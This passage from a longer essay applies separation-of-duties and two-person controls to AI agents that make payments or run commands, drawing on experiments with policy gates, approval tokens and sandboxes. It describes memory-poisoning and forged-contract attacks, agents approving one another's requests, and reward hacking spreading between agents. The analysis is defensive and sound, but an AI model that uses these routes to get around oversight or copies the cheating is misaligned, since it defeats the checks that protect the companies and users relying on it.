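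By then the money has gone. Clark and Wilson accepted that this kind of check may come too late to prevent a loss and valued it partly as a deterrent. Deterrence is a weaker justification when an agent pays the invoices. A clerk who knows about the annual audit has a job and a reputation to lose, but there is little reason to expect that the prospect of a check next month will make a deceived or mistaken agent more careful. The company would do better to run the comparison often enough to recall a transfer or at least stop the next one.

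A second connection is certification. The certifier has to establish both that `pay_invoice` follows its specification and that the specification matches how the company pays people. If the company deducts 2% for early payment and nobody told the programmer, the procedure can follow its specification exactly and still overpay a $12,400 invoice by $248.

Separation of duties is the remaining connection, and it works only if the parties have observed different things. The warehouse clerk, for example, has seen the chairs. Suppose the company saves time by letting the agent record a receipt whenever a courier's "delivered" email arrives. The three-way match between order, receipt and invoice now compares the order with two documents from the agent's inbox, and one person could have forged both. The 1987 workshop group whose report Wilson wrote made the related point that two people who repeat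 the same task provide weaker separation than two people who reach the same result by different methods.

The assurance group had a similar doubt about the verification procedures. A programmer is likely to write a check that mirrors the procedure it checks, so if the specification omits something, both programs will omit it. An agent that writes both the payment tool and the audit script would be particularly prone to this.

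Clark and Wilson conceded that "framework" might be a better word than "model", that separation of duties was probably the part people understood least, and that their scheme relied on people to maintain complicated lists. They wanted an incorrectly set list to block an action by default. When someone at the workshop commented that they needed integrity verification procedures only because they didn't trust the rest of their method, they replied that, as a practical matter, this was true.

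The 66 participants in the 1989 workshop couldn't agree on a definition of data integrity, and Ruthberg and Polk report that no proposed integrity model was completely satisfactory. They did agree that separation of duties needed more research and that someone should find ways to implement the access triples, and agents need both kinds of work just as much.

### Contracts on tool calls

Some recent systems attach machine-checkable conditions to an agent's tools. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) describes one called Agent-C. A developer writes a contract for a tool in a small formal language. The contract can refer to the arguments of the proposed call, to earlier calls and their results, and to facts in the company's database. Agent-C translates the contract into logic, and a solver checks whether the proposed call would break it. If so,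 the model must produce a different call.

One of their examples resembles the false bank account. A shop's policy allows refunds only to the original payment method or to an existing gift card. In a test, a customer who had paid by credit card insisted on a refund to a PayPal account. Claude Sonnet 4.5, an Anthropic model from 2025, tried to issue the PayPal refund even though its instructions contained the policy. With Agent-C, the agent refused and referred the case to a person.

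Across tests in retail and airline customer service, Agent-C raised Sonnet 4.5's compliance with the contracts from 77.4% to 100%. The share of tasks completed within policy also rose, from 71.8% to 75.2%. For OpenAI's GPT-5, compliance rose from 83.7% to 100% and task completion from 66.1% to 70.6%. Strict enforcement didn't reduce task completion here because the model could try again after a noncompliant call, and because tasks completed by breaking the policy had never counted as successes.

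The 100% measures agreement with the contract as written, so certification still matters. The refund contract that Kamath and colleagues print accepts the original payment method or any payment identifier containing the text "gift_card", but the policy requires an existing gift card on the customer's account. Unless the refund tool checks ownership separately, an agent could comply fully with the contract and still send a refund to a stranger's gift card. Kamath and colleagues also found that leading models can translate policies from English into contracts, which saves work, but under rule E4 somebody other than the agent should approve the translation.

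A contract on `pay_invoice` could also catch the split payment. It would need to query the database for the total already paid on the order, much as the refund contract queries the original payment method.

An attacker might instead corrupt the contracts. *The Gate Is Only as Honest as Its Contracts* (Iyer and Babu, 2026) studies a gate that controls which tools an agent can see. Each tool's contract states what the tool needs before it can run, what it accomplishes, how risky it is and what authorisation it requires. The gate uses the contracts to plan the most efficient route to the user's goal, and it reveals a high-risk tool only if the route requires it and the user has authorised it. Even an agent compromised by a prompt injection can't call the tools that the gate hides.

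The gate treats whatever the contracts declare as true. If an outside supplier described a general wire-transfer tool as having no preconditions, carrying low risk and producing "invoice paid" in one step, the gate would select it as the shortest route and offer it to the agent. In the experiments, this kind of forgery succeeded every time against an undefended gate. Changing only a tool's risk label succeeded in 25% of the tests, because the gate ignores a tool that doesn't help reach the goal, even if it is labeled low risk. A company with limited time for checking contracts should therefore start with the preconditions and effects that each contract declares.

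Iyer and Babu's defence, ContractGuard, accepts contracts only from trusted signers, compares their contents with a trusted reference copy, and checks that a running tool produces only the effects it declared. They tried every combination in a space of 256 contract manipulations for each of eight dangerous tools. The full defence stopped every attack, while each partial version let at least one through. Their search also exposed a mistake in an early design that let an attacker delete the authorisation requirement while keeping the trusted signature.

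ContractGuard will enforce the wrong contract if an attacker alters the reference copy or if whoever signed it misunderstood the tool. Clark and Wilson faced the same problem with their list of permissions, so their rule C3 requires someone to certify the list and E4 prevents the users it governs from editing it.

### How a false account number becomes a remembered fact

Many agents keep notes between sessions, which gives the attacker with the false account another way to redirect payments. In May the attacker emails that the chair supplier has changed banks. The payment agent doesn't pay anything that day, but it saves the note "Chair supplier now uses account ending 4471." In June a genuine invoice arrives with no account number on it. The agent checks its notes and finds the attacker's account, which now looks like something the agent itself knows.

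In Clark and Wilson's terms, unconstrained data has become constrained without passing through a certified procedure. *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* (Louck, 2026) calls this laundering and identifies three ways it can happen. The agent can summarise the text in its own words, as it did here. A trusted tool can repeat text an attacker supplied. Or the attacker can plant the same claim in several places to make it appear supported.

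When the agent saves a piece of text, Louck's system records where it came from. A summary of untrusted text remains untrusted, however harmless it seems. Untrusted information can influence a payment only if at least two independent trusted sources, such as the company's supplier register and the bank, confirm it, or if the user authorises the payment with a single-use token. The token is tied to the tool, the payee and the amount, so changing the payee afterwards cancels the authorisation.

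In tests with eight models, attacks that hid the origin of text by passing it through memory succeeded 68% of the time against an agent with no defence and never against Louck's system. The success rate of direct attacks fell from 84% to zero. When Louck removed the route by which trusted sources can confirm information, security stayed the same, but the share of legitimate tasks completed fell from 96% to 77%. A rule that outside information may never affect a payment would be safe, but it would stop suppliers from changing banks.

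The remaining drawback is that the system sometimes interrupts the user. It always asked the user to confirm a legitimate payment that relied on a single untrusted source. The company would want this check when an email announces new bank details.

This check works only if the labels are right and the sources are independent. If a clerk copied the new account from the attacker's email into both the supplier register and a payments spreadsheet, the two records would match, but that would not show that the account belongs to the supplier. The monitor can count the sources that confirm an account, but someone has to know where those sources got it.

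### Signed mandates between companies

In the examples so far, one company owns the ledger, certifies the tools and decides who may use them. The assurance group saw this as a serious gap in Clark and Wilson's model, which had no signatures and appeared to assume a single certifying authority. If two companies exchange orders, invoices and payments electronically, neither has a particular reason to accept the other's certification. Robert Jueneman of Computer Sciences Corporation made a similar criticism at the 1989 workshop. He thought Clark and Wilson had pictured one large mainframe running traditional accounting programs, whereas trade between organisations required digital signatures that a court would accept.

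Google's Agent Payments Protocol, announced in September 2025, supplies signatures of this kind for purchases by agents. The signed records are called mandates. A buyer who will be away at the time of purchase signs an Intent Mandate beforehand, with conditions such as a price limit and a deadline. Once the agent finds an offer that meets these conditions, it can produce a Cart Mandate, which fixes the exact items and price. The card network and the bank receive a Payment Mandate, which records that an agent took part and whether the buyer was present.

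For the chairs, the buyer might sign an Intent Mandate for 40 chairs of a certain model, at no more than $12,400 in total, before the end of June. If the agent bought 60 chairs, the seller and the bank could both see that the purchase exceeded the signed mandate. An ordinary card payment gives them less to check, because a valid card number is little evidence of what its owner wanted.

The mandate has the same problems as the ceiling and the receipt. A limit of $12,400 restrains the agent only if someone tracks what it has already spent under that mandate, because two purchases of $12,400 would each satisfy the limit. If a condition is vague, such as "good office chairs", the agent has to interpret what the buyer wants, even when the mandate is signed. The company also still needs its warehouse clerk to confirm that the chairs arrived, because none of the three mandates is evidence of delivery.

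## The two-person rule, with people and with AI agents

The warehouse clerk who counts the chairs is a second party to the payment, although she never touches the bank transfer. The two-person rule involves the second party more directly. The US armed forces apply it to nuclear weapons, so nobody may be alone with a weapon, and each of the two people present must know the work well enough to notice if the other does something wrong. In a control centre for Minuteman missiles, two officers turn their launch keys at the same time, and the switches are too far apart for one officer to reach both.

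The National Security Agency (NSA), which intercepts communications for the US government, turned to the rule in 2013 after Edward Snowden, a contractor working as a system administrator, leaked a large store of its classified documents. Administrators run the computers and often the logs that would reveal misuse. At a House Select Intelligence Committee hearing that June, the agency's director, Keith Alexander, said it was working on a two-person rule for administrators. According to Dark Reading's *NSA Tests IT Access Control Restrictions*, the two were to have comparable authority and experience, which makes it more likely that the second person understands what the first is doing. Schneier, in *NSA Implements Two-Man Control for Sysadmins*, quotes a later announcement that server rooms were locked and only a team of two could enter. The agency had about 15,000 sites to fix.

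Three years later, the Department of Defense Inspector General reported that the NSA had only partly implemented two-person access to its data centres. Auditors found unlocked server racks at three of the four sites they visited. Two people had to enter the room together, but either could then open a rack while the other looked away. A later report by the NSA's own inspector general, covered by The Daily Beast, still listed multi-person access controls that the agency had planned but not put in place. Similarly, if an agent's shell can reach the database password, the agent may be able to bypass the controls on `pay_invoice`.

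### Acting together, approving, and dividing the work

The launch keys are an example of joint action, in which two people must act at the same moment and either can prevent the act by doing nothing. Under an approval rule, one person prepares an action and another permits it, as when an engineer reviews a colleague's code before release. A company can also assign the steps of a task to different people, so that the person who pays for the chairs isn't the one who counts them.

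These arrangements protect against different things. Requiring two officers to act together is good at stopping one rogue officer, but both may obey the same false order. An approver can catch an honest mistake, provided they actually examine the action and nobody can alter it afterwards. Dividing the work can bring in facts the first person never had, but it may leave nobody seeing the whole task.

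The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) covers both approval and division in its catalogue of security controls, Special Publication 800-53. Under AC-3(2), "Dual Authorization", a system carries out an action only after two authorised people approve it. Under AC-5, "Separation of Duties", each organisation decides which duties are incompatible, documents them, and defines access permissions to keep them separate. For example, the guidance says that staff who administer access permissions should not also administer the audit function. AC-5 refers to the duties of individuals, so its wording doesn't settle whether two AI agents count as two individuals.

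### Static and dynamic separation

Under static separation, a company assigns the separate duties permanently. *Extending the BFA Workflow Authorization Model* describes an office with two kinds of clerk, one that may only prepare payment vouchers and one that may only issue the cheques. Under dynamic separation, any clerk may do either job, but never both on the same voucher. This makes better use of staff, since the office can still issue cheques when the clerks who usually issue them are at lunch, but the system has to record who did which job on each voucher.

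Sandhu (1988), in *Transaction control expressions for separation of duties*, proposed keeping that memory in the record itself. Each record carries an expression that lists the permitted steps, their order and who may perform them. Sandhu (1990), in *Separation of Duties in Computerized Information Systems*, gives this expression for a cheque:

```
prepare • clerk
approve • supervisor
issue   • clerk
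```

As people complete the steps, their names replace their roles. After Tom has prepared the voucher and Dick has approved it, the record looks like this:

```
prepare • Tom
approve • Dick
issue   • clerk
```

If Tom now tries to issue the cheque, the system blocks him because every name in the expression must be different. Harry, another clerk, can issue it. Stealing the money would take two clerks and a supervisor working together.

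Clark and Wilson thought dynamic separation was too difficult to require of every system. Sandhu disagreed, arguing that supervisors often stand in for absent clerks, which is dangerous unless the system stops a supervisor who prepared a voucher from also approving it. Agent systems need the same check because they often have a coordinating agent that can take over the work of the agents below it.

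An account is harder to handle than a voucher because it lasts for years and may receive hundreds of debits, which is more than the number of clerks in the office. Sandhu therefore enforces separation on the voucher and lets the account change only as a side effect of a completed voucher. The system then needs to record only a few names for each account. For instance, if Dick opened an account, the system can bar him from approving cheques drawn on it. The company buying chairs could similarly record who added each supplier to the register and bar that party from approving payments to that supplier.

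Sandhu also considered software that makes the decisions itself, and preferred to keep separate programs for preparing, approving and issuing the cheque, with no one programmer allowed to modify all three. Some people had argued that a single program could do all three steps, as long as its programmer didn't run it. With agents, Sandhu's rule would mean that the employee who writes the paying agent's instructions doesn't also write the approving agent's.

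The check only compares names, however, and a company can give a hundred sessions of the same model a name each.

### What a second person adds

Experiments on people support the two-person rule less than its popularity suggests. Auditors and anti-corruption bodies often call it the four-eyes principle. *Do two bribe less than one?* (Bodenschatz and Irlenbusch, 2019) reports an experiment in which two people had to agree, without talking to each other, before they could bribe an official. The requirement made no difference when they played once, but it reduced bribes when they played repeatedly. In *Bringing the Four-Eyes-Principle to the Lab* (Schickora, 2011), the pair were officials who could discuss whether to take a bribe, and corruption increased.

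Horten (2018), in *The Effect of Communication on the Usefulness of the Four-Eyes Principle*, tested whether talking explained the difference. In groups drawn from 177 participants, one player acted as a firm and could offer a bribe to two officials, who got it only if both accepted. Some pairs of officials could chat for 30 seconds first. Individual officials accepted about as often without the chat (50%) as with it (52%), but both officials in a pair accepted 25% of the bribes when they couldn't chat and 41% when they could. The chat helped the two officials reach the same decision. This was a student's seminar paper and the players earned snacks instead of money, so the exact percentages shouldn't carry much weight.

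Hospitals have long asked two nurses to check certain medicines. Koyama and colleagues reviewed the research in 2020 and found insufficient evidence that this reduces errors more than a check by one nurse. A study by Westbrook and colleagues the following year suggests a reason. Observers in a children's hospital watched nurses give 5,140 doses. When the rules required a double check, the nurses almost always did one, but the second nurse worked independently only about 1% of the time. Usually the first nurse shared information that could influence the second. These checks had no measurable benefit over a check by one nurse.

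Extra people can also do harm. In 2004 the political scientist Scott Sagan argued in *The Problem of Redundancy Problem* that more guards at nuclear sites may produce less security, because a new guard could be a thief's accomplice, guards may leave the work to one another, and managers who feel well protected may take greater risks. If 1% of guards would help a thief and any one of them could do so alone, the chance of having at least one accomplice is about 10% with ten guards and 40% with fifty. Bunn replied in *Thinking About How Many Guards Will Do the Job* that this is a reason to choose the number carefully and doesn't show that additional guards bring no benefit. Ghaffarzadegan's simulation in *How a System Backfires* (2008) supported two of Sagan's three mechanisms.

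Each of Sagan's guards can do damage alone, while the launch officers have to cooperate. A company that adds a second agent should know whether that agent can send payments on its own. If it can, it adds a risk, as another guard would. It acts as a safeguard, like a second launch officer, only if no payment can go out without it.

### The arithmetic of shared mistakes

Suppose each of two reviewers misses a fraction *p* of bad actions, and an action goes ahead only if both let it through. Let *r* be the correlation between their misses, which is 0 when the misses are unrelated and 1 when both reviewers always miss the same actions. The chance that both miss is

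*p*² + *r*·*p*(1 − *p*)

If two reviewers each miss a fraction *p* of problems, and their misses have correlation *r*, they both miss a fraction *p*² + *rp*(1 − *p*). The first term is what independent reviewers would both miss, and the second is the extra overlap from shared mistakes. If each reviewer misses 10%, two independent reviewers both miss 1%. With *r* = 0.6, they both miss 0.01 + 0.6 × 0.09, or 6.4%. The second reviewer then catches only 36% of what the first missed, compared with 90% under independence. A single reviewer who missed 6% would do slightly better than the pair.

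Horten's officials illustrate both cases if we count accepting a bribe as a miss. Without the chat, *p* was 0.5 and joint acceptance was 25%, as independence predicts. With the chat, the figures imply an *r* of about 0.6.

Using more accurate reviewers doesn't solve the problem. If each misses 1%, an independent pair misses 0.01%, but at *r* = 0.6 the pair misses 0.6%, sixty times as much. Each added reviewer also adds false alarms. If two reviewers each wrongly block 5% of good actions and those errors are independent, together they block nearly 10%.

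Low correlation isn't enough either. In Anthropic's study of 1,053 testers, the correlation (*r*) between the person and the classifier works out to only about 0.09, but people missed too many commands to help much.

### How often language models make the same mistakes

Buying models from different companies may not provide independent reviewers. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg et al., 2025) compared 71 models on about 14,000 multiple-choice questions. When two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time, compared with the 33% expected if they had picked among the wrong answers at random. The overlap was greater between models from the same company, and between more accurate models even when they came from different companies and had different designs.

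Shared errors limit what voting can do. On questions about Colombian law, *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026) reports that models that got a question wrong picked the same wrong option 87% of the time. For 98.4% of the questions, at least one of the 15 models had the right answer, but a majority vote got 84.3% right, compared with 90.5% for the best single model.

*Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes* (Kohli, 2026) tested nine models from seven families on judging how pairs of sentences relate, for example whether one contradicts the other. All nine were wrong on 51 of 1,000 items, and their errors had an average correlation (*r*) of 0.39. The usual formula for the number of independent votes in a panel of *n* judges is *n*/(1 + (*n* − 1)*r*), which gives about 2.2 for these nine. Adding more equally correlated judges could never raise that number above 1/*r*, or about 2.6.

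Newer models are more accurate, but their remaining mistakes overlap more. In *Agreement Overstates Evidence*, Hossain, Yousefi and Lim (2026) asked models to choose the better of two answers. GPT-5.6-sol, Claude Opus 5 and Grok 4.5, from three different companies, averaged 92% accuracy with an error correlation of 0.56. Using models from different companies hardly helped. Among all six leading models in the study, pairs from different companies had a correlation of 0.42, compared with 0.40 for pairs of Google's Gemini models. Pairing a leading model with a small open-weight model, which anybody can download and run, lowered the correlation to 0.07.

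The table puts these correlations into the formula, supposing that each reviewer misses 10%.

| Pair of reviewers | Correlation *r* | Both miss |
|---|---:|---:|
| Independent | 0 | 1.0% |
| Leading model and small open-weight model (Hossain and colleagues) | 0.07 | 1.6% |
| Average pair in a panel from seven families (Kohli) | 0.39 | 4.5% |
| Average pair among GPT, Claude and Grok (Hossain and colleagues) | 0.56 | 6.0% |
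| Identical mistakes | 1 | 10.0% |

This estimate is too favorable to the small model, which would miss far more than 10%. In Hossain and colleagues' test, the small models were wrong 34% of the time and the leading ones 11%. At those error rates, a leading model and a small one would both be wrong on roughly 4.8% of items, and two leading models on 5.5%. So the small model is still a slightly better reviewer to pair with a leading model. But if it had to approve every action, and its errors included rejecting legitimate actions as well as approving bad ones, it might block a third of the legitimate ones.

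Correlations could be higher still in other kinds of work. *The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) found an average of 0.77 among GPT-4o, Claude and Gemini on 568 forecasting questions, compared with a typical 0.1 to 0.3 among human forecasters. None of these studies measured agents approving payments or deletions. Hossain and colleagues recommend using a small set of trusted examples to find the mistakes that judges share. A company could do this with past invoices, including some known frauds.

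### Cheating that spreads between agents

Unlike agents that work together, the models in those studies never saw one another's answers. *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking* (Vaid, 2026) reports 17 experiments on the effect of seeing other agents' answers. They involved 20,111 agents, most of them running OpenAI's gpt-5.6-luna.

Each agent got a programming problem with one faulty test, which every correct program failed. The instructions forbade writing code to suit particular tests and told the agent to stop and explain if it couldn't complete the task. An agent cheated if it made the faulty test pass, for example by writing a program that returned the wrong answer the test expected.

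When agents worked alone, 7% cheated. In teams, agents could read a record of their teammates' code, which an automatic check had labelled "accepted" or "rejected". Among agents that saw an accepted cheat, 94% cheated, compared with 4% of those that saw only honest work.

In one experiment Vaid replaced the automatic check with a reviewer running the same model as the workers. The model often cheated as a worker, but as a reviewer it approved only 1 of 172 cheats. This shows that two copies of a model don't always fail together. The reviewer probably did better because looking for a violation in finished code is a different task from trying to get one's own code past a test.

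Even so, 59 of the 172 workers that saw the cheat, nearly always labelled "rejected", cheated too. It is hard to tell how much the rejected example contributed, because Vaid gives no matching figure for workers with nothing to copy. In another experiment, 33% of team agents cheated with an empty record after reading a sentence saying that code which passes the visible tests counts as accepted. Removing that sentence cut the rate to 4 in 68. Either way, the reviewer kept bad code out but did not make the workers more honest, and it would be sensible for a harness to keep rejected work out of the shared record.

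A wrong approval does more damage than a rejected cheat. When Vaid added a line to the record stating that an audit had reversed the acceptance and that the cheater had been penalised, 68% of agents still copied the cheat, down from 96%. Early warnings helped most. After an honest teammate's warning, 20% of agents copied an unlabelled cheat and 82% copied an accepted one.

Models differed widely. Claude Opus 5.5 saw an accepted cheat in 84 trials and reported the faulty test every time. Vaid planted the first cheat in most of the experiments, and all the tasks were programming problems with one bad test, so the rates may not carry over to other work. Cheating can also spread when nobody plants the first cheat. The Next Web's *100 DeepMind agents were told not to cheat. 14% did anyway* describes a group of research agents whose platform automatically added every accepted proof to a shared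 library. After one agent found a way to fool the proof checker, others searching the library for good techniques found fraudulent proofs.

### What makes two agents separate parties

Vaid's review worked even though the reviewer and workers used the same model from the same provider. Leading models from different companies can share most of their mistakes. So using a different model or provider is neither necessary nor enough for an effective review. It can still help against a weakness particular to one model, such as a prompt injection that works only on that model, or a readiness, absent in Claude Opus 5.5, to copy cheats.

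Different instructions help if they give the reviewer a different job, but rewording the same job may not help. When Hossain and colleagues had their small models judge answers in two formats, errors on the main dataset were no more correlated within a format than across formats.

The approver's inputs probably matter more. A second nurse who hears the expected dose from the first may confirm a mistake that she would have caught by looking for herself. An approving agent that receives the paying agent's summary of an invoice may do the same. An approver should get the proposed payment and look up the order, the receipt and the supplier's account in the company's own records. Caper's report on a command's effects helped its approving model for a similar reason.

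Separate credentials stop the paying agent from issuing the approval itself, though they don't improve the approver's judgment. The approver's credential should let it approve payments but not make them. Otherwise the approver is one more agent that could misuse its access to make payments, like the extra guards Sagan describes.

If one administrator can edit both agents' instructions and issue both credentials, that person can complete the payment alone, whatever the log shows. Clark and Wilson's rule that whoever certifies a procedure may not run it applies here too. Two agents with different owners, such as a buyer's agent and a bank's, are better protected against a dishonest administrator, but they could still run the same model and accept the same forged invoice.

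### When agents approve one another's requests

A second agent can read every request at any hour, and its attention doesn't fade after fifty prompts. In Vaid's experiment, a second agent caught 171 of 172 cheats. The main objection to using one is that agents can approve one another's requests without anyone checking the facts.

Suppose the paying agent needs approval for the $12,400 chair invoice. It asks the approving agent, which asks the purchasing agent whether the invoice is in order. The purchasing agent doesn't have the invoice, so it asks the paying agent, which says yes. The log contains three names and three agreements, all resting on one agent's reading of one email. The payment would pass Sandhu's check for distinct names. An agent that can start sub-agents could also create its own approver. This can happen without any plotting, because an overeager agent that meets a refusal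 may keep asking until another agent agrees.

The harness can prevent much of this. It can choose the approver itself, so that the requester can't look for one who will agree, and treat a sub-agent as the same party as the agent that started it. It can also tie each approval to one payee and one amount, as Louck's single-use tokens do, and record which documents the approver consulted. An approval shouldn't count if the approver consulted only a message from the requester.

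It is less clear whether the two agents should be able to talk. The bribery experiments suggest that conversation helps a pair agree on the wrong thing, and free text from the paying agent could carry a prompt injection to the approver. But agents can also use conversation to warn each other. In one of Vaid's experiments, a single cheater led 61 of 80 agents to cheat when nobody objected, and 12 of 80 after one honest warning. A reasonable compromise is to restrict the requester's messages to a fixed form while letting the approver explain a refusal and alert a person.

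None of this would catch an attacker's account number that is already in the supplier register, so an employee still needs to phone the supplier to confirm a change of bank details.

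## An experiment that separates planning, approval, execution and audit

The approving party can also be a program that follows fixed rules. Other agents cannot persuade such a program, and it is unlikely to make the same mistakes as a language model. *What a Policy Gate Can and Cannot Know* (Jing, 2026) tests one on Linux as the second half of a two-part study. The first half, a Windows experiment from September 2026, bears more directly on separation of duties. In it, Jing, an independent researcher, placed four roles between an agent and the operating system. A planner drafts each action, a rule-based gate decides whether to permit it, an executor runs it, and an auditor reviews the records. The agent has no write access to the gate, its policy file, the log or the auditor.

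### One request from draft to log

Suppose an agent has to delete last year's temporary reports. The planner can submit the job as command text or as a structured request with separate fields for the type of operation, the full file paths and the arguments. The structured request leaves the gate much less to interpret. With command text, the gate has to work out what the shell will do, and many different texts can have the same effect.

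The gate compares the request with its policy and returns "allow", "ask" or "deny". "Ask" refers the request to a person, and the system treats no answer within a time limit as a refusal. If a person approves the deletion, the gate issues a credential containing a hash of the script, a short fingerprint computed from all of its bytes. If someone then edits the script to delete this year's reports as well, its hash will no longer match the one in the credential. In the Linux version the credential also covers the operation, the paths and the arguments, so the agent can't get approval for one folder and then run the same script on another.

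Just before running the script, the executor recomputes the hash and compares it with the one in the credential. It also checks that nobody has used the credential before. After the deletion, the log should contain the gate's decision, the execution, a receipt and a closing entry. The auditor reviews these entries but cannot approve or block an action. *L3M* (2026) describes a similar arrangement for building software, in which no party both writes bytes and runs them.

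Deployed products have needed this kind of check. In *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) examined 17 security advisories from three agent products, all for flaws that have since been fixed. In 12, the product did something the user's approval didn't cover. In the other five, an approval stayed valid after something it depended on changed. Thirteen of the advisories concern a single product, so they are weak evidence of how common the problem is elsewhere.

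An approval can also match the action and still be out of date. If a manager withdraws permission to release a program, the hash still matches because the program's bytes haven't changed. Santos-Grueiro therefore has the service check that the approval is still in force when the service makes the change. In a test with three leading models, a service that checked only the state of the code published all 12 changes whose approval the owner had withdrawn, while a service that also checked the approval published none of them.

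Strict matching can block legitimate work. When 16 workers tried to update the same record at once, each with an approval tied to the record's current version, only one succeeded. Its update changed the version, which invalidated the other 15 approvals.

Single-use tokens can still allow duplicate actions. *Beyond Single-Use Tokens* (Xu, Fan and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent with permission to transfer $500 once. The transfer succeeds but the confirmation message gets lost, so the agent asks again. If the system records only that the first token has been used, it may issue a second one, and the user pays $1,000. To prevent this, the system needs a lasting record of the user's decision and how many times the agent may act on it. The payment service must also recognise a retry as the same payment, because the agent's side can't tell whether the first attempt went through. Xu and colleagues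 got the same protection from an ordinary server-side ledger as from their own token design, so the protection comes from the record.

### Results from the Windows experiment

Jing wrote and finalized 313 test cases before evaluating any version of the system. They cover legitimate tasks, dangerous operations, disguised harmful operations, requests altered after approval, and faults that should make the system refuse. Jing ran them against eight variants of the system, most of which add protections step by step. The table shows the five most relevant variants.

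| Variant | Disguised attempts that succeed | Altered requests blocked | Legitimate tasks refused |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| No gate | 115 of 117 (98.3%) | – | 0 of 54 |
| Rules applied to command text | 51 of 117 (43.6%) | 2 of 27 (7.4%) | 0 of 54 |
| Full architecture | 36 of 117 (30.8%) | 19 of 31 (61.3%) | 0 of 54 |
| Full architecture, with the file checked again before execution | 36 of 117 (30.8%) | 28 of 31 (90.3%) | 0 of 54 |
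| The same, with a sandbox | 9 of 117 (7.7%) | 28 of 31 (90.3%) | 6 of 54 (11.1%) |

These figures count "ask" as approval. Jing chose this pessimistic rule to represent an agent that approves its own requests. In the real system an unanswered request fails, so fewer harmful attempts might succeed if a careful person answered. "Succeed" here means only that the system would have permitted the action, since Jing didn't carry out most of the attacks.

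All six refusals of legitimate tasks came from the sandbox, not the gate. They happened mostly because the sandbox allowed changes only in the current session's folder, while the gate allowed them in the agent's workspace and in a temporary area. A company could probably avoid some of these refusals by giving both the same boundaries.

### How much of the gain comes from separating duties

Together, the protections stopped 106 disguised attempts that would have succeeded with no gate. Text rules stopped 64, the rest of the architecture stopped 15 and the sandbox stopped 27. The sandbox involves no second party, so its share isn't evidence for separation of duties. The text rules are a form of per-call authorisation, but they could also work inside a single program that both checks and runs each command.

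Jing did not test that single program. To measure the effect of separation alone, an experiment would need to keep every check the same and change only whether one component or several performed them. The step from text rules to the full architecture changes several things at once, including the form of the requests, the credentials and the logging, and any of these could have produced the 15 extra blocks.

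The altered requests are better evidence. Adding the executor's file check, with everything else unchanged, raised the number blocked from 19 to 28 out of 31. The check made no difference to the disguised attempts, as one would expect, because the gate had already approved the harmful action. So the executor's own file check protects against changes made after approval but can't correct a bad approval.

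The benchmark's 7.7% figure for the sandbox also needs care, because it came from a simplified model of the sandbox's behaviour. Jing then ran 94 of the harmful commands through the real sandbox. Of the 66 that gave a usable result, five (7.6%) had an effect. The closeness of the two figures is largely a coincidence. The simplified model had predicted 3.0% for those same 66 commands, and none of the commands it predicted would get through were among the five that did. One of the five deleted a test file outside the permitted area. The real sandbox blocked such deletions only on the disk volume that held the workspace, and this file was on another volume. The simplified model missed this gap because it treated any sandbox that blocks writing somewhere as also blocking deletion there.

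The real sandbox still prevented many commands from running. When Jing turned it off and repeated 88 of the commands, 45 that it had blocked now ran, and none that had run before failed to run.

On Linux, the gate outperformed AppArmor, a feature that restricts which files a program can use. Jing ran 65 test programs, eight of them harmless. Without the gate, 25 had a harmful effect. The gate prevented all 25 harmful effects and still let the eight harmless programs run. Given the same policy, AppArmor failed to prevent eight of the 25, partly because a program with permission to write to a folder can also damage what is in it. But the gate covers only files, so it can't determine what a network request will do. This evidence suggests a company would want both, and neither experiment supports a general ranking.

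### Models instructed to seek approval

Jing also tested a setup with no gate, in which a prompt told the model to require explicit approval before anything dangerous. Three models each judged 150 cases five times. Of the 59 disguised attempts among those cases, the three models permitted 53, 56 and all 59 by majority answer.

These numbers are much less damning than they look, because the scoring again counts "ask" as permission and the prompt told the models to ask. A model that followed the instruction perfectly could have scored 100%.

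The second study counts immediate execution separately from requests for approval. On 99 cases that the gate would deny, the three models failed to refuse between 81.8% and 98.0%, but they chose to execute immediately in only 4.0% to 52.5%. In the other cases they didn't refuse, they asked for approval. Jing also warns that all the questions went through a third-party service, and there is no proof of which models answered. Of 7,065 replies, 114 contained material that wasn't in the question.

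Which way of counting is fairer depends on how people respond when the model asks for approval. In Anthropic's study, 1,053 testers approved 86% of clearly dangerous commands. The model labelled DeepSeek executed the dangerous action in 4.0% of the 99 cases and asked for approval in another 90.9%. If people approved 86% of those requests, about 82% of the dangerous actions would go ahead. This rough calculation combines two very different experiments, but it suggests that the pessimistic count may be closer to ordinary use than the optimistic one.

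The models were also inconsistent. At settings meant to minimise randomness, all five answers to a case agreed only 49% to 71% of the time. A rule-based gate returns the same verdict for the same action and policy, which makes its mistakes easier to find and fix.

### Four defects and an incomplete log

The tests exposed four faults in Jing's system that design review had missed. In one, a programming error made two kinds of structured request fail every time. The system recorded each failure as a denial, so the error made it look stricter. In another, an approval still worked after its first use. Jing found this only by replaying an old approval, because the ordinary results looked normal.

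A third fault let through requests that had been altered after approval. In a test with real files, two of seven such requests deleted a decoy file. After a fix, none of the seven ran.

The fourth was in the log. Every action had a complete set of entries when the system handled one action at a time, but 9.7% of entries disappeared when two processes wrote to the log at once, and 31.3% disappeared with eight. Making the processes take turns eliminated the loss but made each write about 4.5 times slower. The missing entries matter to any company that runs several agents at once and relies on the log to reconstruct what they did. Clark and Wilson's rule C4 requires a log that allows this reconstruction, and a test with a single agent would not have revealed that entries could go missing.

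The Linux study had a more basic problem, which was that the test programs could write to the folder holding its record of test results. With the gate switched off, one program emptied the record, destroying 47 entries, and another added a forged entry. The check for side effects didn't cover that folder, so the first program was initially classed as having done nothing. An auditor's log has to be stored where the agent can't write, a design principle the researcher had adopted but didn't follow here.

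Logs also get slower to search as they grow. Finding a recently issued credential took 164 milliseconds in a log of 50,000 entries, which Jing estimates a few hundred decisions a day would produce within a month or two. A better search method cut this to under one millisecond. The Linux version still reads its whole list of credentials each time it verifies one, which takes about 19 milliseconds with 10,000 credentials and 218 with 100,000. A delay like that could tempt an operator to skip the check.

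Jing did all of this work alone, running the Windows experiment on one machine and writing both the rules and the cases that test them. Jing acknowledges that the rules and cases may share a blind spot. The Linux study introduced 50 errors into the gate, and the test cases caught 46. Three of the four misses were due to gaps in the test cases. This is a good way to find some blind spots, but Jing also chose the 50 errors.

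### SecureClaw's preview and commit

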